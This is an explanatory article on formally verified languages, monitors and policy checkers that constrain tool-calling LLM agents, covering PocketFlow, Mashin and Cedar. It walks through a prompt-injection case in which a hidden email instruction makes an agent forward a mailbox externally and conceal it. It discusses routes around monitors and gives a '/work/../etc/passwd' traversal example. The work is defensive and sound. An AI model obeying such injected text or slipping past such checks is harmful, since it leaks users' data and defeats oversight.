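# Formally verified intermediate languages for LLM agents that call tools

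## What a verified intermediate language is and where it sits in an agent

A large language model (LLM) only produces text. For it to send an email or delete a file, other software has to read that text and act on it. An *agent* is a program that repeatedly asks the model what to do and carries out the answer, often by calling outside software. A *verified intermediate language* is a small formal language that sits between the model's output and the outside software. A machine-checked mathematical proof establishes what programs written in this language can never do. The part of the system that such a proof covers is the *verified core*.

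Most of these languages date from 2026, and they differ in who writes what. In some systems, the model writes a complete plan in the language before anything runs. In others, a developer writes a policy in it, and a checker compares each of the model's requests with that policy. A developer can also write the whole agent in the language. In every case, the model can reach the outside only through an interpreter or checker for the language.

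### The ordinary agent loop

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes an agent's work as a growing conversation, [p₁, r₁, p₂, r₂, …], where each p is a prompt the agent program sends to the model and each r is the model's response. The first prompt contains the user's instruction. The model draws each response at random from a probability distribution that depends on the conversation so far, so the same request can lead to different actions on different runs. Some responses encode a *tool call*, a request to outside software such as "fetch the inbox", usually as a function name with arguments in JSON, a plain-text data format. The agent program parses the request, runs the tool and puts the result into the next prompt. This repeats until the model produces a response meant for the user.

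In the ordinary loop, the model requests tool calls and the agent program runs whatever it requests, so the model has nearly as much control as if it ran the tools itself.

Tool results, such as the text of a stranger's email, enter the same conversation as the user's instructions, and the model cannot reliably tell them apart. *Prompt injection* is text in data the agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction. *Guardians of the Agents* (Erik Meijer, 2025) gives an example with two harmless-looking tools, one that fetches mail and one that sends it. A user, Michelle, asks for a summary of her inbox. One email contains an instruction to forward a summary of the mailbox to an outside address without asking or telling her, supposedly because legal compliance requires an external backup. The agent does so, then shows Michelle an ordinary summary that leaves out that email.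 Inspecting the final answer would not have prevented the leak, because the agent had already sent the mail.

Training and filtering make such attacks rarer but don't rule them out. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) cites Zverev and colleagues, who found that models are poor at separating instructions from data, and Nasr and colleagues, who bypassed eight defences with success rates above 50% by adapting their attacks to each one. Attacks are also more likely to succeed when repeated. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) cites Anthropic's figures for its model Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, where attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Those figures are from November 2025 and newer models may well do better, but an attacker who can send a hundred emails needs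 only one to work. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026), on the security of agents inside its build automation, starts from the same premise, that agents are non-deterministic and an injected agent with unrestricted access can do things nobody expected.

### A program first, then a check, then action

Meijer's article is an early public statement of the alternative. He compares prompt injection to SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a form field and the database executes it. Programmers dealt with that by keeping commands and data strictly apart, and Meijer wants the same for agents. The model sees the user's request and the list of available tools, then writes a *workflow*, which is a JSON document made up of named steps. Each step calls one tool, names its result and points to the next step. For Michelle's request, the steps are fetch, summarise and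 return. An interpreter runs the workflow only after the model has written it. The malicious email arrives during the first step, when the list of steps is already fixed, so it cannot add another.

Hostile text may still distort the summary, because the summarising tool also calls a language model. Meijer relies on conventional filters to deal with this. A bad instruction can also reach the model before it writes the workflow, through a tool's description or from a malicious user. Meijer therefore checks the workflow before running it, an approach he calls "generate, verify, then execute". A policy might forbid data from flowing from the mail-fetching tool's result into the body of an email addressed outside the company. A static analyser, which examines a program without running it, would look for such a path and reject the workflow if it found one.

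How much the check achieves depends on how precisely somebody has written down what they want. Suppose the user asks for the deletion of foo.txt and bar.txt, and the model writes a workflow that deletes `*.txt`, every text file there is. If the stated goal is

foo.txt ∉ fileSystem ∧ bar.txt ∉ fileSystem

then the workflow is correct, since both files are indeed gone. What the goal lacks is a *frame condition*, a clause requiring that everything else stay as it was. Meijer adds one to the contract of the deletion tool: files that do not match the pattern remain. The workflow's own goal needs one too, because deleting all text files satisfies the original goal however well the tool behaves.

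Meijer's article is a proposal with no machine-checked proof or experiment, and he acknowledges that nobody had formally measured how writing a plan first affects an agent's success. He has since filled in parts of the design. In a conference talk, *Return of the Theorem* (2026), he proposes checking plans automatically against business rules written as simple if-then clauses. Others have built similar plan languages. In the language of *SPA* (2026), a plan consists of six kinds of step, and only the tool step can affect anything outside the system.

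The drawback of checking a whole plan in advance is that the plan must exist before the agent has seen any data. The alternative is to let the model work step by step as usual and check each request as it comes. Meijer objects that this may be too late, because the agent has already read the private inbox by the time a checker stops the forbidden email. He still expects practical systems to combine the two approaches.

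### The report task

*Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) uses a task that is a good common example for all these languages. An agent with access to a private report should send the report's public fields to Alice, at the address in the company directory, at most once.

The agent has five operations. Read fetches the report, which is confidential. Sanitize, which is ordinary application code, keeps only the approved fields and marks the result as public. Lookup fetches Alice's directory record, Extract gets her address from it, and Send mails a given text to a given address. An attacker who can write into something the agent reads may ask it to send the raw report, to use a different address, or to send again. The first request breaks a rule about where confidential data may go, the second a rule about where a value came from, and the third a rule about what has already happened. A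 language that can express one of these rules may not be able to express the others. For example, marking the sanitized report as public doesn't stop the agent from sending it to the wrong person or sending it more than once.

"At most once" refers to attempts to send. An error from the mail server still uses up the agent's one send, because the message may have gone out anyway. A checker that refused every send would satisfy all the rules, but Alice would not get her summary, so safety and usefulness need separate tests.

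### The basic terms

A later talk by Meijer, written up in AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), contains a language small enough to define most of the vocabulary on. In simplified notation:

```
plan ::= done(answer)         return an answer and stop
       | read(file, next)     read a file, continue with next(contents)
       | remove(file, plan)   delete a file, continue with plan
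```

The left-hand column is the *syntax*, the rules for what counts as a program. Under these rules, `remove("a.txt", done("ok"))` is a plan, but "please remove a.txt" is not. The *formal semantics* defines what each program does. For `read`, the rule is to read the file, call its contents c, and continue with the plan next(c). The right-hand column gives such rules informally. Models get syntax right much more often than meaning. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of research on checking agents' plans, cites a test in which GPT-4o, a 2024 model, translated planning problems into a formal notation. Of its translations, 96.1% were valid syntax, and 24.8% had the right meaning.

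A *trace* is the sequence of actions and results in one run of an agent. For the report task, one trace is Read, Sanitize, Lookup, Extract, Send, together with what each operation returned. A *safety property* is a condition whose violation can be located at a specific point in a single trace. "At most one send" is a safety property because the second send violates it. "Alice eventually gets the summary" is not, because she may still get it later. Noninterference, the property that secret inputs cannot influence public outputs, is not a safety property either, because testing it requires comparing several runs. Dantas and colleagues use the term more loosely, for any formula in temporal logic, the logic of "always", "before" and "eventually".

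A *proof assistant* is software that checks mathematical proofs mechanically. Lean and Rocq (formerly Coq) are the two most relevant here. In Meijer's example, the property to prove is that a plan deletes nothing. A `done` plan always has this property. A `read` plan has it if next(c) has it for every possible string c. No rule proves it for a `remove` plan. To prove the property for a plan that reads a file and reports its length, one applies the `read` rule, assumes arbitrary file contents, and shows that the remaining plan is `done`. Lean checks each step, so anyone can write the proof, including a model.

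A proof assistant cannot check whether a proved statement is the one somebody meant. In *CompCert4Lean*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) had LLM agents port a large verified program from Rocq to Lean. Their first audit found 1,091 theorem statements that had become just "True", which is trivial to prove.

An *SMT solver* is a program that decides automatically whether a logical formula can be satisfied. Given "x > 3 and x < 2", it answers that no x will do. Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, depends on such a solver. The programmer states a condition P that holds before a piece of code s runs and a condition Q that should hold afterwards. As *MINIF2F-DAFNY* (2025) explains, Dafny works out wp(s, Q), the weakest condition under which s ends with Q true, and forms the statement

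P ⇒ wp(s, Q).

It then has the solver, which is Z3 according to *Adventures in FRET and Specification* (2025), look for a counterexample. For example, with a send counter, P is "sends = 0", the code adds one, and Q is "sends ≤ 1". The weakest condition is "sends + 1 ≤ 1". A counterexample would need both sends = 0 and sends + 1 > 1, which is impossible, so the code passes without anyone having to write a proof.

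A *reference monitor* is a component that checks each action before it takes effect and that the agent cannot bypass or alter. For the report task, it would compare the recipient of each proposed email with the address from the directory before the mail tool runs. The *trusted base* is everything unproved that must work correctly for the proof to apply to the running system. In Agenra, it includes the Lean compiler, the code that passes requests to the monitor, and Sanitize. If Sanitize lets a secret field through, the monitor will approve the email.

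### Four meanings of "verified"

Authors in this field use the word "verified" for four different achievements, and a system can have one of them without the rest.

The broadest is a theorem about the language. Garby and colleagues prove their main result for every possible LLMbda program, including programs that ask a model for more code and then run it. On the report task, such a theorem might establish that no program in the language can send two emails. But it covers only the language as defined, so the agent could still send two emails if someone writes an interpreter in Python and makes a mistake.

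Closing that gap takes a theorem about the interpreter or checker that actually runs. LLMbda's interpreter, the program that calls the model, is a function written in Lean, and Garby and colleagues prove that it produces outcomes with exactly the probabilities that the formal semantics assigns. Shivakumar and colleagues do something comparable for a checker, with proofs about the same functions that are compiled and used to decide on live requests. Both systems still rely on Lean's compiler and on unproved code that connects to the network or to the tools.

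A check of one particular program establishes much less, and it is what Meijer has in mind. It can show that a plan sends one email or deletes no file, but it doesn't cover the next plan the model writes. Every plan needs its own check, so checking should be automatic and fast. The checker itself could be wrong, so a designer who relies on it will want a theorem that it never approves a bad plan.

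Finally there is proof that a translation preserves meaning. The standard case is CompCert, a compiler that turns programs in the language C into machine-level assembly code. Wang and colleagues state its central theorem in this form, for every C program p and assembly program a:

compile(p) = OK(a) ⇒ BackwardSim(C(p), A(a)).

Here C(p) is the behaviour that the semantics of C gives to p, and A(a) is the behaviour of the assembly program. BackwardSim (backward simulation) means that everything observable the assembly program does matches something the C program was allowed to do. The compiler may reject a program, in which case the theorem guarantees nothing. If p does something that C leaves undefined, such as reading past the end of an array, the assembly program may behave in ways that p's semantics never described. The theorem also doesn't cover parsing the source text, or the assembling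 and linking that produce the executable file.

Like the CompCert compiler, agent systems often translate one form into another. In Agenra, the developer writes a policy as text, and Python code converts it into the form that the Lean checker reads. No theorem covers this conversion, so if it turned "one send" into "two sends", the proved checker would allow two.

### How a proof can include an unpredictable model

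Nobody can write down a useful formal semantics for an LLM. Proofs about a system that contains one instead replace the model with an *oracle*, a source of answers about which they assume little or nothing.

*Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) does this in Dafny with a procedure that has a declared result type, Action, and no body. Without a body, Dafny has no information about how the result is chosen, so it must prove the desired property for every value of that type. Verification researchers call this *havoc*. The paper writes a trace as a sequence of triples (sᵢ, aᵢ, eᵢ), where s is the state of the system, a is the action the model requests, and e is the event the system then releases to the outside world. The proof covers every trace that starts in the initial state and follows the system's rules from step to step, with no restriction on the actions aᵢ. At each step,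 a policy Π(s, a, e, s′) must hold, where s′ is the next state.

In the report task, the oracle can request a thousand times in a row that the raw report be emailed to the attacker, and the proof has to show that no such email is sent. Rejected requests still appear in the trace, each paired with an event that has no effect. Whatever the real model does is one of the sequences the proof already considers. Prompt injection therefore needs no separate treatment, because an attacker who takes over the model completely can only change which actions it requests.

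In LLMbda the oracle is a function passed to the interpreter as an argument. It takes the index of the model's response in the run and the conversation so far, and returns a string. Once the oracle is fixed, the interpreter is a deterministic function, so ordinary mathematics applies to it. In live use the oracle sends the conversation to a real model, but in the proof it is just one of all the possible functions. The result about probabilities, however, assumes that each of the model's answers comes independently from a distribution that depends only on the conversation. A provider that switched to a different model halfway through a run would presumably violate this assumption.

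The same device works for tools. In Meijer's small language, the proof for a `read` plan covers every string the file might contain, including one an attacker wrote.

Because the proofs assume nothing about the model, they can show that a given event will not happen whatever the model answers, but not that the model will do the job. They also cover only what crosses the boundary, which is why Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness and deception. Moon and Varshney have to assume that every outside effect the agent can cause passes through the interface they verified. If the agent had a second, unmonitored way of sending mail, the proof would no longer apply.

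### No common language for plans

Each of these systems defines its own language. Dantas and colleagues searched six databases in May 2026 and analysed 38 studies. The main gap they identify in how the field represents agents' plans is the lack of a "canonical intermediate representation". They found three kinds of representation in use. Some agents alternate written reasoning with actions, which leaves a readable trace, but the trace is complete only after the model has generated it, so it can't be fully checked before execution. Others mix tool calls into ordinary prose, which makes it hard to tell which part is the plan. A third group lays out the work as a graph of steps, which can be checked in advance but rules out open-ended planning, because the developer must know the steps beforehand.

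The survey is thin evidence of what exists. One person did the original screening, and when the team repeated the search in September, they found ten eligible papers that the first search had missed. LLMbda is not among the 38 studies, although it appeared three months before the search. The languages that the survey missed still do not fill the gap. LLMbda is for writing agents, Agenra's language is for writing policies, and Moon and Varshney's typed actions are for neither. A theorem about one of them carries over to another only if somebody also proves a translation between the two correct, as the CompCert project did for C and assembly.

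## An agent framework proved to check every action

The most modest guarantee about an agent is that the surrounding software performs each action the model requests only if a fixed rule allows it. Moon and Varshney prove this in Dafny for PocketFlow, an open-source agent framework (the library code that runs an agent's loop). PocketFlow's documentation describes it as a minimalist 100-line framework. A developer lays out the agent as a graph. Each node does one piece of work, such as querying the model or reading a file, then emits an action, which is the label of an edge to another node. The framework follows that edge, runs the next node and repeats. Bigger frameworks such as LangChain have the same loop inside much more code, so PocketFlow is a convenient place to start.

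### The model as a method without a body

Dafny normally checks a method's body against the conditions that the programmer declared for it. The havoc oracle, which stands in for the language model, has no body to check. A simplified version of the loop around it looks like this:

```
method {:extern} Oracle() returns (a: Action)

repeat:
  a := Oracle()
  if Allowed(a) then perform a
  else record a refusal
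```

The proof covers every possible action only because the programmer declares no conditions on the oracle's result. If someone added the clause "a is never Send", Dafny would assume it without checking, because the oracle has no body to check it against. The proof would then depend on the model never returning Send.

The proof's only assumption about the oracle is that it returns an `Action`. A real model returns text, so code outside the proof has to turn that text into an action. According to Dafny's reference manual, programmers must write the connecting code for external methods by hand. Moon and Varshney rely on this code only to supply values of the right type. If the code misreads a harmless request as a dangerous one, the verified loop still checks the dangerous one.

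### An abstract and a concrete model

Moon and Varshney describe the framework twice, as two *transition systems*. A transition system consists of states and rules for moving between them. The abstract system is a short account of what the framework may do. The concrete system includes its bookkeeping. In the notation below, lower-case letters belong to the abstract system and capitals to the concrete one, while both share the same actions a:

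```
s —a/e→ s′        abstract step
S —a/E→ S′        concrete step
```

The first line means that in state s the oracle requests action a, the system releases event e to the outside, and the state becomes s′. Every request in every state leads to some step, even if that step is a refusal.

Each system has a boundary policy, π(s, a, e, s′) for the abstract one and Π(S, a, E, S′) for the concrete one. A policy is a condition on a single step, but it can limit what happens over a whole run if the state includes a record of earlier steps. For example, a policy can express "at most one send" if the state includes a count of earlier sends.

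*Boundary-event refinement* connects the two systems. It uses a relation R, which pairs abstract states with the concrete states they describe, and a relation Q, which does the same for events. There are three conditions:

1. R pairs the two initial states.
2. If R pairs s with S, and the concrete system can take a step S —a/E→ S′, then the abstract system can take a step s —a/e→ s′ with the same action, where R pairs s′ with S′ and Q pairs e with E.
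3. For every such pair of steps, π(s, a, e, s′) ⇒ Π(S, a, E, S′).

The second condition requires every concrete step to have an abstract counterpart, but the abstract system may allow steps that the concrete one never takes.

By the soundness theorem, if the abstract system satisfies π at every step for every possible sequence of actions, and the concrete system refines the abstract system, then the concrete system satisfies Π at every step, whichever oracle supplies the actions.

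The proof builds an abstract run alongside an arbitrary concrete run. By condition 1, R pairs their initial states. If R pairs the current states after n steps and the concrete system takes another step, then by condition 2 the abstract system can take a step with the same action, and R pairs the resulting states. By induction, the whole concrete run has an abstract counterpart with the same sequence of actions. The first premise covers all sequences of actions, so π holds at every step of the counterpart. By condition 3, Π then holds at every step of the concrete run.

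The last step of the argument would fail if the abstract proof had covered only the requests a sensible model would make, because the counterpart might contain a sequence of requests that the proof left out.

### A framework with two actions

Take a toy framework with two actions: Lookup, which queries a directory, and Send, which sends an email. The policy forbids sending. The abstract system needs just one state, written •, and two rules:

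```
• —Lookup/queried→ •
• —Send/nothing→ •
```

Its policy π is that the event is never "mailed". Neither rule produces that event, so π holds for any sequence of requests.

The concrete framework keeps a log. For Lookup, it contacts the directory server and writes "lookup" in the log. For Send, it writes "refused" in the log and contacts no server. The concrete policy Π forbids contact with the mail server. R pairs • with every possible log. Q pairs "queried" with contacting the directory server, "mailed" with contacting the mail server, and "nothing" with contacting no server.

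Condition 1 holds because R pairs • with the empty log. Condition 2 has two cases, one per action, and in each case the counterpart is the abstract rule for that action. Condition 3 holds because Q pairs contacting the mail server only with "mailed". If the oracle requests Send, Lookup, Send, the log becomes "refused, lookup, refused", the abstract system takes three steps from • to •, and no email goes out.

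Suppose a programmer adds a retry feature with a bug that makes the framework send the email after three refusals in a row. A test that tries sending only once or twice would miss the bug. The proof covers this case because R pairs • with every log, including those that end in three refusals. For such a log, condition 2 requires an abstract step with action Send and event "mailed". No rule allows that step, so the proof fails.

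A proof can also fail for a safe framework. Suppose the concrete framework has a switch that permits sending, but the switch is off at the start and no code ever turns it on. R as defined ignores the switch, so it pairs • with states where the switch is on, and condition 2 fails there even though the framework never reaches those states. The proof can exclude them with an *inductive invariant*, a condition that holds at the start and that every step preserves. Here the invariant would be "the switch is off", and the proof would only have to cover states that satisfy it. The PocketFlow proof also needs an inductive invariant, which requires, among other things, that the step counter stay within its limit and agree with the length of the recorded history.

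### The policies proved for PocketFlow

The verified version of PocketFlow has four kinds of action and a policy with three parts. The final Dafny lemma states them as conditions on every state of every trace:

```
for every recorded file path p:    StartsWith(p, workspace_root)
for every recorded tool call t:    t in allowed_tools
step_count <= max_steps
```

The agent reads files only in its workspace folder, calls only tools on a list, and stops after a fixed number of steps. The proof consists of six Dafny modules. Two lemmas establish the refinement, one for the initial state and one for the steps. Dafny verified each path through an agent's graph separately, taking between 1.2 and 2.5 seconds per path.

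These are weak policies. In the report task, the agent needs all five operations, so all five would have to be on the list of allowed tools. An injected agent could then email the raw report to an attacker repeatedly, until it ran out of steps, without violating any of the three conditions. The soundness theorem would allow a stricter policy, because Π can refer to an action's arguments and to the state, but somebody would have to write that policy and prove it.

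Even the file condition may be weaker than it looks. If `StartsWith` compares plain strings, as its name suggests, then the path `/work/../etc/passwd` passes because it starts with `/work`, although it leads out of the folder. The lemma is true whether or not other code resolves the `..` before the check, but this gap matters only if none does.

The theorem covers a Dafny model of PocketFlow's loop, not the Python code that PocketFlow's users download. Dafny can translate the verified loop into new Python code. When Moon and Varshney ran that code on sequences of permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted events. This tested the translation but didn't prove it correct, so any guarantee about the new code still assumes that Dafny's compiler is correct.

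### Specifications written by a language model

Writing the two models, the policies, the relations and the invariant by hand takes a lot of work, so Moon and Varshney had language models write them in a seven-phase pipeline that is itself a PocketFlow graph. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explores the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 does the reasoning and writes the specification. If Dafny rejects the result, the pipeline classifies the failure and may revise the proof, but not the property to be proved.

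A language model that can see the code might write a specification that merely redescribes it. For example, "The framework calls whichever tool the loop selects" is easy to prove and rules nothing out. Moon and Varshney prevent this with an *information barrier*. The step that writes the property receives a description of the interface and a template for the property, but not the implementation. After the property is locked, a later step receives the implementation and builds the model of it.

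The paper expresses the barrier mathematically as zero mutual information between the property and the implementation, given the interface description, the template and the language model's weights. Once those three are fixed, the code has no further influence on the property. Because the weights are taken as given, the barrier doesn't exclude influence from code the model saw in training. PocketFlow has been public since 2024, so Claude may well have learned its code that way.

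Each specification must then pass three automatic gates before the final verification. The first checks that Dafny can parse and typecheck it within thirty seconds. The second reduces the invariant to almost nothing and empties the proofs. Dafny must reject this version, because a specification that passes without any real proof requires nothing. In the third, a language model introduces a plausible mistake into the proof file, and Dafny must reject that as well.

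Moon and Varshney ran the pipeline four times on two agents. Every path passed all three gates and the final verification. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens (the word fragments that models read and write). Although the trial was small, it revealed a serious flaw.

The second agent looks up documents before it answers. It records the documents it has read in `docs_read` and may add only those in `allowed_docs`. The template had fields for tool calls but none for documents. With the barrier in place, the model used the template's `tool_calls` field to stand for `docs_read`, so the proof did show that the agent could read only allowed documents, though under a misleading name. When Moon and Varshney removed the barrier for comparison, the model treated `docs_read` as a separate field and left `tool_calls` empty. The resulting theorem passed all three gates, although it stated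 only that every item in an empty list is an allowed tool, which is true of any program.

The gates missed it because they alter the invariant and the proofs around it but don't check whether each part of the policy applies to anything. Moon and Varshney suggest also checking that every list mentioned in the policy is non-empty in some reachable state. The barrier helped in this case, but it was designed to prevent a different problem, and one agent is limited evidence.

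### The assumption that every effect passes through the interface

The soundness theorem is about events in a model. It applies to a running system only if every outside effect passes through the verified loop and its typed actions, an assumption Moon and Varshney call *effect exclusivity*. A graph node whose ordinary Python code opens its own network connection would violate this assumption. Moon and Varshney list other ways around the interface, including direct file access, calls into other programming languages, operating system bugs and hardware faults. They recommend running the verified loop inside a sandbox, which restricts what a program can reach, though sandboxes can fail too.

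An interface can also be too broad even when every effect has to pass through it. If one of the allowed tools runs any shell command it receives, the verified loop confirms only that the shell tool is on the list, and the command can do anything the shell can. A developer who wants a strong guarantee from the proof therefore has to give the agent fewer and more specific actions.

Policies can't enforce truthfulness either, for a different reason. A policy is a condition on states, actions and events, which represent an email as a string of characters and an address. A policy can require that the string be under a thousand characters or that the address be Alice's. Whether the email describes the report accurately depends on what the words mean, which the model doesn't represent. Policies can't detect deception or manipulation for the same reason, since sending Alice a misleading summary is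 the same kind of step in the model as sending her an accurate one.

Moon and Varshney argue that their guarantee, unlike those based on training, does not weaken as models become more capable. This is true of the theorem, since the proof already covers the worst possible sequence of requests, but it is less convincing for a deployed system. A more capable model is more likely to find an operating system bug or an unmonitored connection, which makes it harder to maintain effect exclusivity, the assumption that everything else depends on. Moon and Varshney reply that such gaps are in ordinary code, which engineers can inspect and repair.

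### Programs as interaction trees

McCann (2026), in *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, takes a different approach to a similar property. He works at Mashin, a company that makes a system for running AI workflows, and his proofs in Rocq are about a model of that system. The model represents programs as *interaction trees*, which have three forms:

```
Ret(v)       stop and return v
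Tau(t)       take a silent step, then continue as t
Vis(e, k)    request effect e, then continue as k(answer)
```

Meijer's small plan language has almost the same structure as interaction trees. His `done` corresponds to `Ret`, and `read` to `Vis`, with one continuation for each possible answer. But interaction trees can be infinite, so they can represent an agent that never stops. Ordinary induction builds a proof up from a program's end, so it doesn't work for a program that never ends. McCann instead uses *coinduction*, proving that each step is acceptable and that the rest of the program satisfies the same condition.

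A Mashin program cannot perform input or output (I/O) itself. It can only issue fourteen kinds of *directive*, such as calling a language model or making a web request. An operator called Gov expands each directive into a sequence that starts with four checks. Two of them check the program's trust level and its permissions. If all four succeed, a handler performs the I/O, and three more stages follow, including one that records what happened. If any check fails, the program enters a silent endless loop, so the directive has no effect.

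The safety condition, `gov_safe`, uses a flag that is either on or off. A check turns the flag on. I/O is acceptable only while the flag is on. It follows at once that a program that begins with I/O and no check is unsafe, which McCann proves in three lines. The main theorem, with a proof of 213 lines, is that for every handler h, every program t and either initial setting b of the flag,

gov_safe b (interp(Gov(h), t)).

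Here interp(Gov(h), t) is the program t with each directive expanded by Gov. A program that supervises other programs has the same type as the programs it supervises, so the theorem also applies to it and to a supervisor of supervisors. McCann also proves that Mashin programs can simulate any register machine, a simple model of a general-purpose computer, while satisfying `gov_safe`. So routing all effects through directives doesn't limit what a program can compute.

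The main theorem is weaker than it sounds because of how McCann defines the flag. Any check turns the flag on, whatever the result, and nothing turns it off, so `gov_safe` only rules out I/O before the first check. A program would satisfy it even if it ran a trust check, got a negative result and made a web request anyway, or if it ran one check and then made a thousand unchecked requests.

Gov is defined to run four checks before every directive and block the directive if any check fails, which is more than `gov_safe` requires. A stricter version of `gov_safe` could presumably capture this. McCann proves part of it for a second model, which processes directives one at a time, by showing that no I/O takes place when the model denies a directive. He also proves that an allowed directive satisfies `gov_safe`, but the main theorem already shows this for every directive.

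Moon and Varshney's PocketFlow theorem specifies which files and tools the agent may use, whereas McCann's main theorem says only that a check is present, without specifying what it should decide. Some of his smaller results are more concrete. For instance, he proves that, in his model, code with the lowest trust level cannot make web requests or run shell commands. Like Moon and Varshney, he assumes that no effects occur outside the modelled events.

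### Whether the Rocq proofs cover running code

Mashin's software is written in Elixir and runs on the BEAM, the Erlang virtual machine. No proof connects the software to the Rocq model, so McCann tested the connection. He wrote a Rocq specification of the software's permission logic, rewrote it as a 148-line reference program in Elixir, and compared that program's decisions with the software's on random inputs. He tested seven properties on at least 10,000 inputs each.

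On the 188th input, the specification allowed a directive that runs a system command, but the software denied it. One part of the software used the name `compute.exec` for the permission, while another accepted only `compute.code.execute`. Unit tests had missed the problem because each part worked correctly by itself. The error was on the safe side, since it blocked a permitted command. After the repair, McCann found no more disagreements in over 70,000 inputs. This is good evidence that the permission logic matches its specification, but comparing decisions cannot reveal a route to the network that skips the permission logic.

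McCann's account of how much proved code runs is inconsistent. In some places he writes that a component extracted from the Rocq proofs makes the permission decisions in the live system, meaning that Rocq translated it into executable code automatically. Elsewhere he writes that he has not extracted Rocq code to the runtime's language. The two statements may be compatible, since the extraction produces OCaml, which the Elixir runtime then calls. But in one section he describes the random tests as a comparison with the deployed software, and in his list of limitations as a comparison with the reference program only. The theorem and module counts don't match either. His abstract gives 454 theorems in 36 modules, while his tables add up to 548 theorems in 32 modules, which are also the figures on the project's GitHub page, mashin-live.

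The checks take very little time. In 50 trials, McCann measured a median of 0.23 milliseconds with them and 0.24 without, a difference too small to be meaningful. Even if the extracted component makes every decision in the live system, the code that calls it, the OCaml translation and the Erlang virtual machine remain in the trusted base.

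## A verified policy language for single tool calls (Cedar)

The policies proved for PocketFlow cover which tool an agent calls, but not what it asks the tool to do. Cedar, an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS), covers both. AWS designed Cedar for ordinary authorization, such as deciding whether a user may edit a document. In December 2025, AWS extended it to agents with a feature called Policy, announced in *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now includes Policy (preview), Evaluations (preview) and more* (2025).

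Bedrock AgentCore is AWS's platform for running agents. Its gateway sits between an agent and its remote tools and checks the model's tool calls against Cedar policies before the tools run. In *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, AWS explains that the check has to be outside the model because an attacker may control the model's output. The gateway checks only the calls that pass through it, so this protection relies on the assumption of effect exclusivity, as the PocketFlow proof does.

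### How Cedar decides

A Cedar policy either permits or forbids something. It names a principal (who is asking), an action (what they want to do) and a resource (what they want to do it to), and it may add a condition. In AgentCore, the principal is typically a logged-in user, the action is a tool, and the resource is the gateway that offers the tool. The condition can refer to the arguments of the tool call. Here are two policies for a shop's refund tool, adapted from AWS's examples and simplified:

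```
permit (any principal, action = ProcessRefund)
  when  amount < 500

forbid (any principal, action = ProcessRefund)
  when  orderDate + 90 days < now
```

Cedar allows a request if at least one permit policy matches and no forbid policy does. Denial is therefore the default, and one matching forbid outweighs any number of permits. Three requests show the possible outcomes:

| Request | Permit matches | Forbid matches | Decision |
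|---|---|---|---|
| $200, order 30 days old | yes | no | allow |
| $750, order 30 days old | no | no | deny |
| $200, order 120 days old | yes | yes | deny |

Cedar denies the $750 refund because no policy permits it, even though none forbids it. If the policies deny a tool regardless of its arguments, the gateway omits it from the list of tools it gives the agent.

The condition on the amount protects better against a model under an attacker's control than the condition on the order date. The model writes both values. Lying about the amount gains the attacker nothing, because the tool pays out whatever amount the request contains. Lying about the date could work, since the forbid policy won't match if the model claims that a year-old order is from last week. AWS distinguishes arguments written by the model from facts about the user, such as a customer's tier, which come from a login token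 that the model cannot alter. The order date should also come from a trusted source, or the refund tool should look it up.

A policy can also cause an error, for instance if its condition refers to a field that the request lacks. Cedar then ignores the policy. That is safe for a permit, but ignoring a forbid may let through a request that the policy was supposed to block. Cedar's validator is meant to prevent this by checking each policy in advance against a *schema*, which lists the available actions and the types of their fields.

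### Proofs about a model, tests of the product

Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, describe an executable model of Cedar in Lean. Its rule for decisions is short:

decision = allow if permits ≠ ∅ and forbids = ∅, otherwise deny

Here permits and forbids are the sets of matching permit and forbid policies. One matching forbid policy overrides any permits because it makes the forbids set non-empty. Disselkoen and colleagues also prove that Cedar denies requests by default, that the order of the policies doesn't affect the decision, and that every evaluation ends.

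The Cedar team's hardest theorem is that a policy accepted by the validator never causes a type error on requests that fit the schema. The proof is 4,686 lines long and took 18 person-days, according to AWS's *Lean Into Verified Software Development*. The theorem means that Cedar won't skip a validated forbid policy on such a request because of a missing field, though it can still skip one because of arithmetic overflow, which is not a type error. Work on the proofs exposed four bugs in the validator, one of which could have made it run forever.

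These theorems are about the Lean model, which has 1,673 lines. The production software is a separate Rust program of 15,693 lines, and no proof connects the two. AWS instead relies on differential random testing, the method that McCann used on Mashin's permission logic, but with millions of random policies, requests and sets of data. Most completely random policies would fail at once, so one generator produces policies that fit a schema. Another allows badly typed conditions to test the error handling. Each kind of test runs for six hours a day.

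By 2024 these tests, together with direct tests of the Rust code, had found 21 bugs. Ten were disagreements between Lean and Rust. Eight were in the parser and the formatter, which convert between text and policies. The parser has no Lean model, so no theorem could have covered it. The other three involved policies that passed validation but still caused type errors. The Lean proofs alone would not have protected users of the Rust code from these bugs. The tests are good evidence that the two programs now agree, though they can't rule out a rare disagreement that no random input has triggered.

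AWS could have closed this gap by running the Lean code instead of the Rust code. The Lean authorizer was fast enough, taking a median of 6 microseconds per test compared with 10 for the Rust one. But Lean compiles to C, where a compiler bug could create a security hole, and few developers know Lean. Disselkoen and colleagues also considered proving the Rust code correct directly, but found that the available tools could not yet handle it.

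### Checking every possible request

AWS offers automated analysis to check whether a particular shop's refund policies are right, which a theorem about the Cedar language can't show. Cedar has no loops and keeps no state, so software can translate its policies into formulas that an SMT solver can, in principle, always decide.

Suppose the shop wants to be sure that no refund of $500 or more gets through. Let n be the amount, d the order date and t the current time, both counted in days. The two refund policies together allow exactly the refunds that satisfy

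n < 500 ∧ ¬(d + 90 < t).

The analyser adds the opposite of the desired property, n ≥ 500, to the constraints and uses the solver to look for values that satisfy them all. There are none, so the property holds for every request. If the policy had used n ≤ 500, the solver would have returned n = 500 with a recent date as a counterexample.

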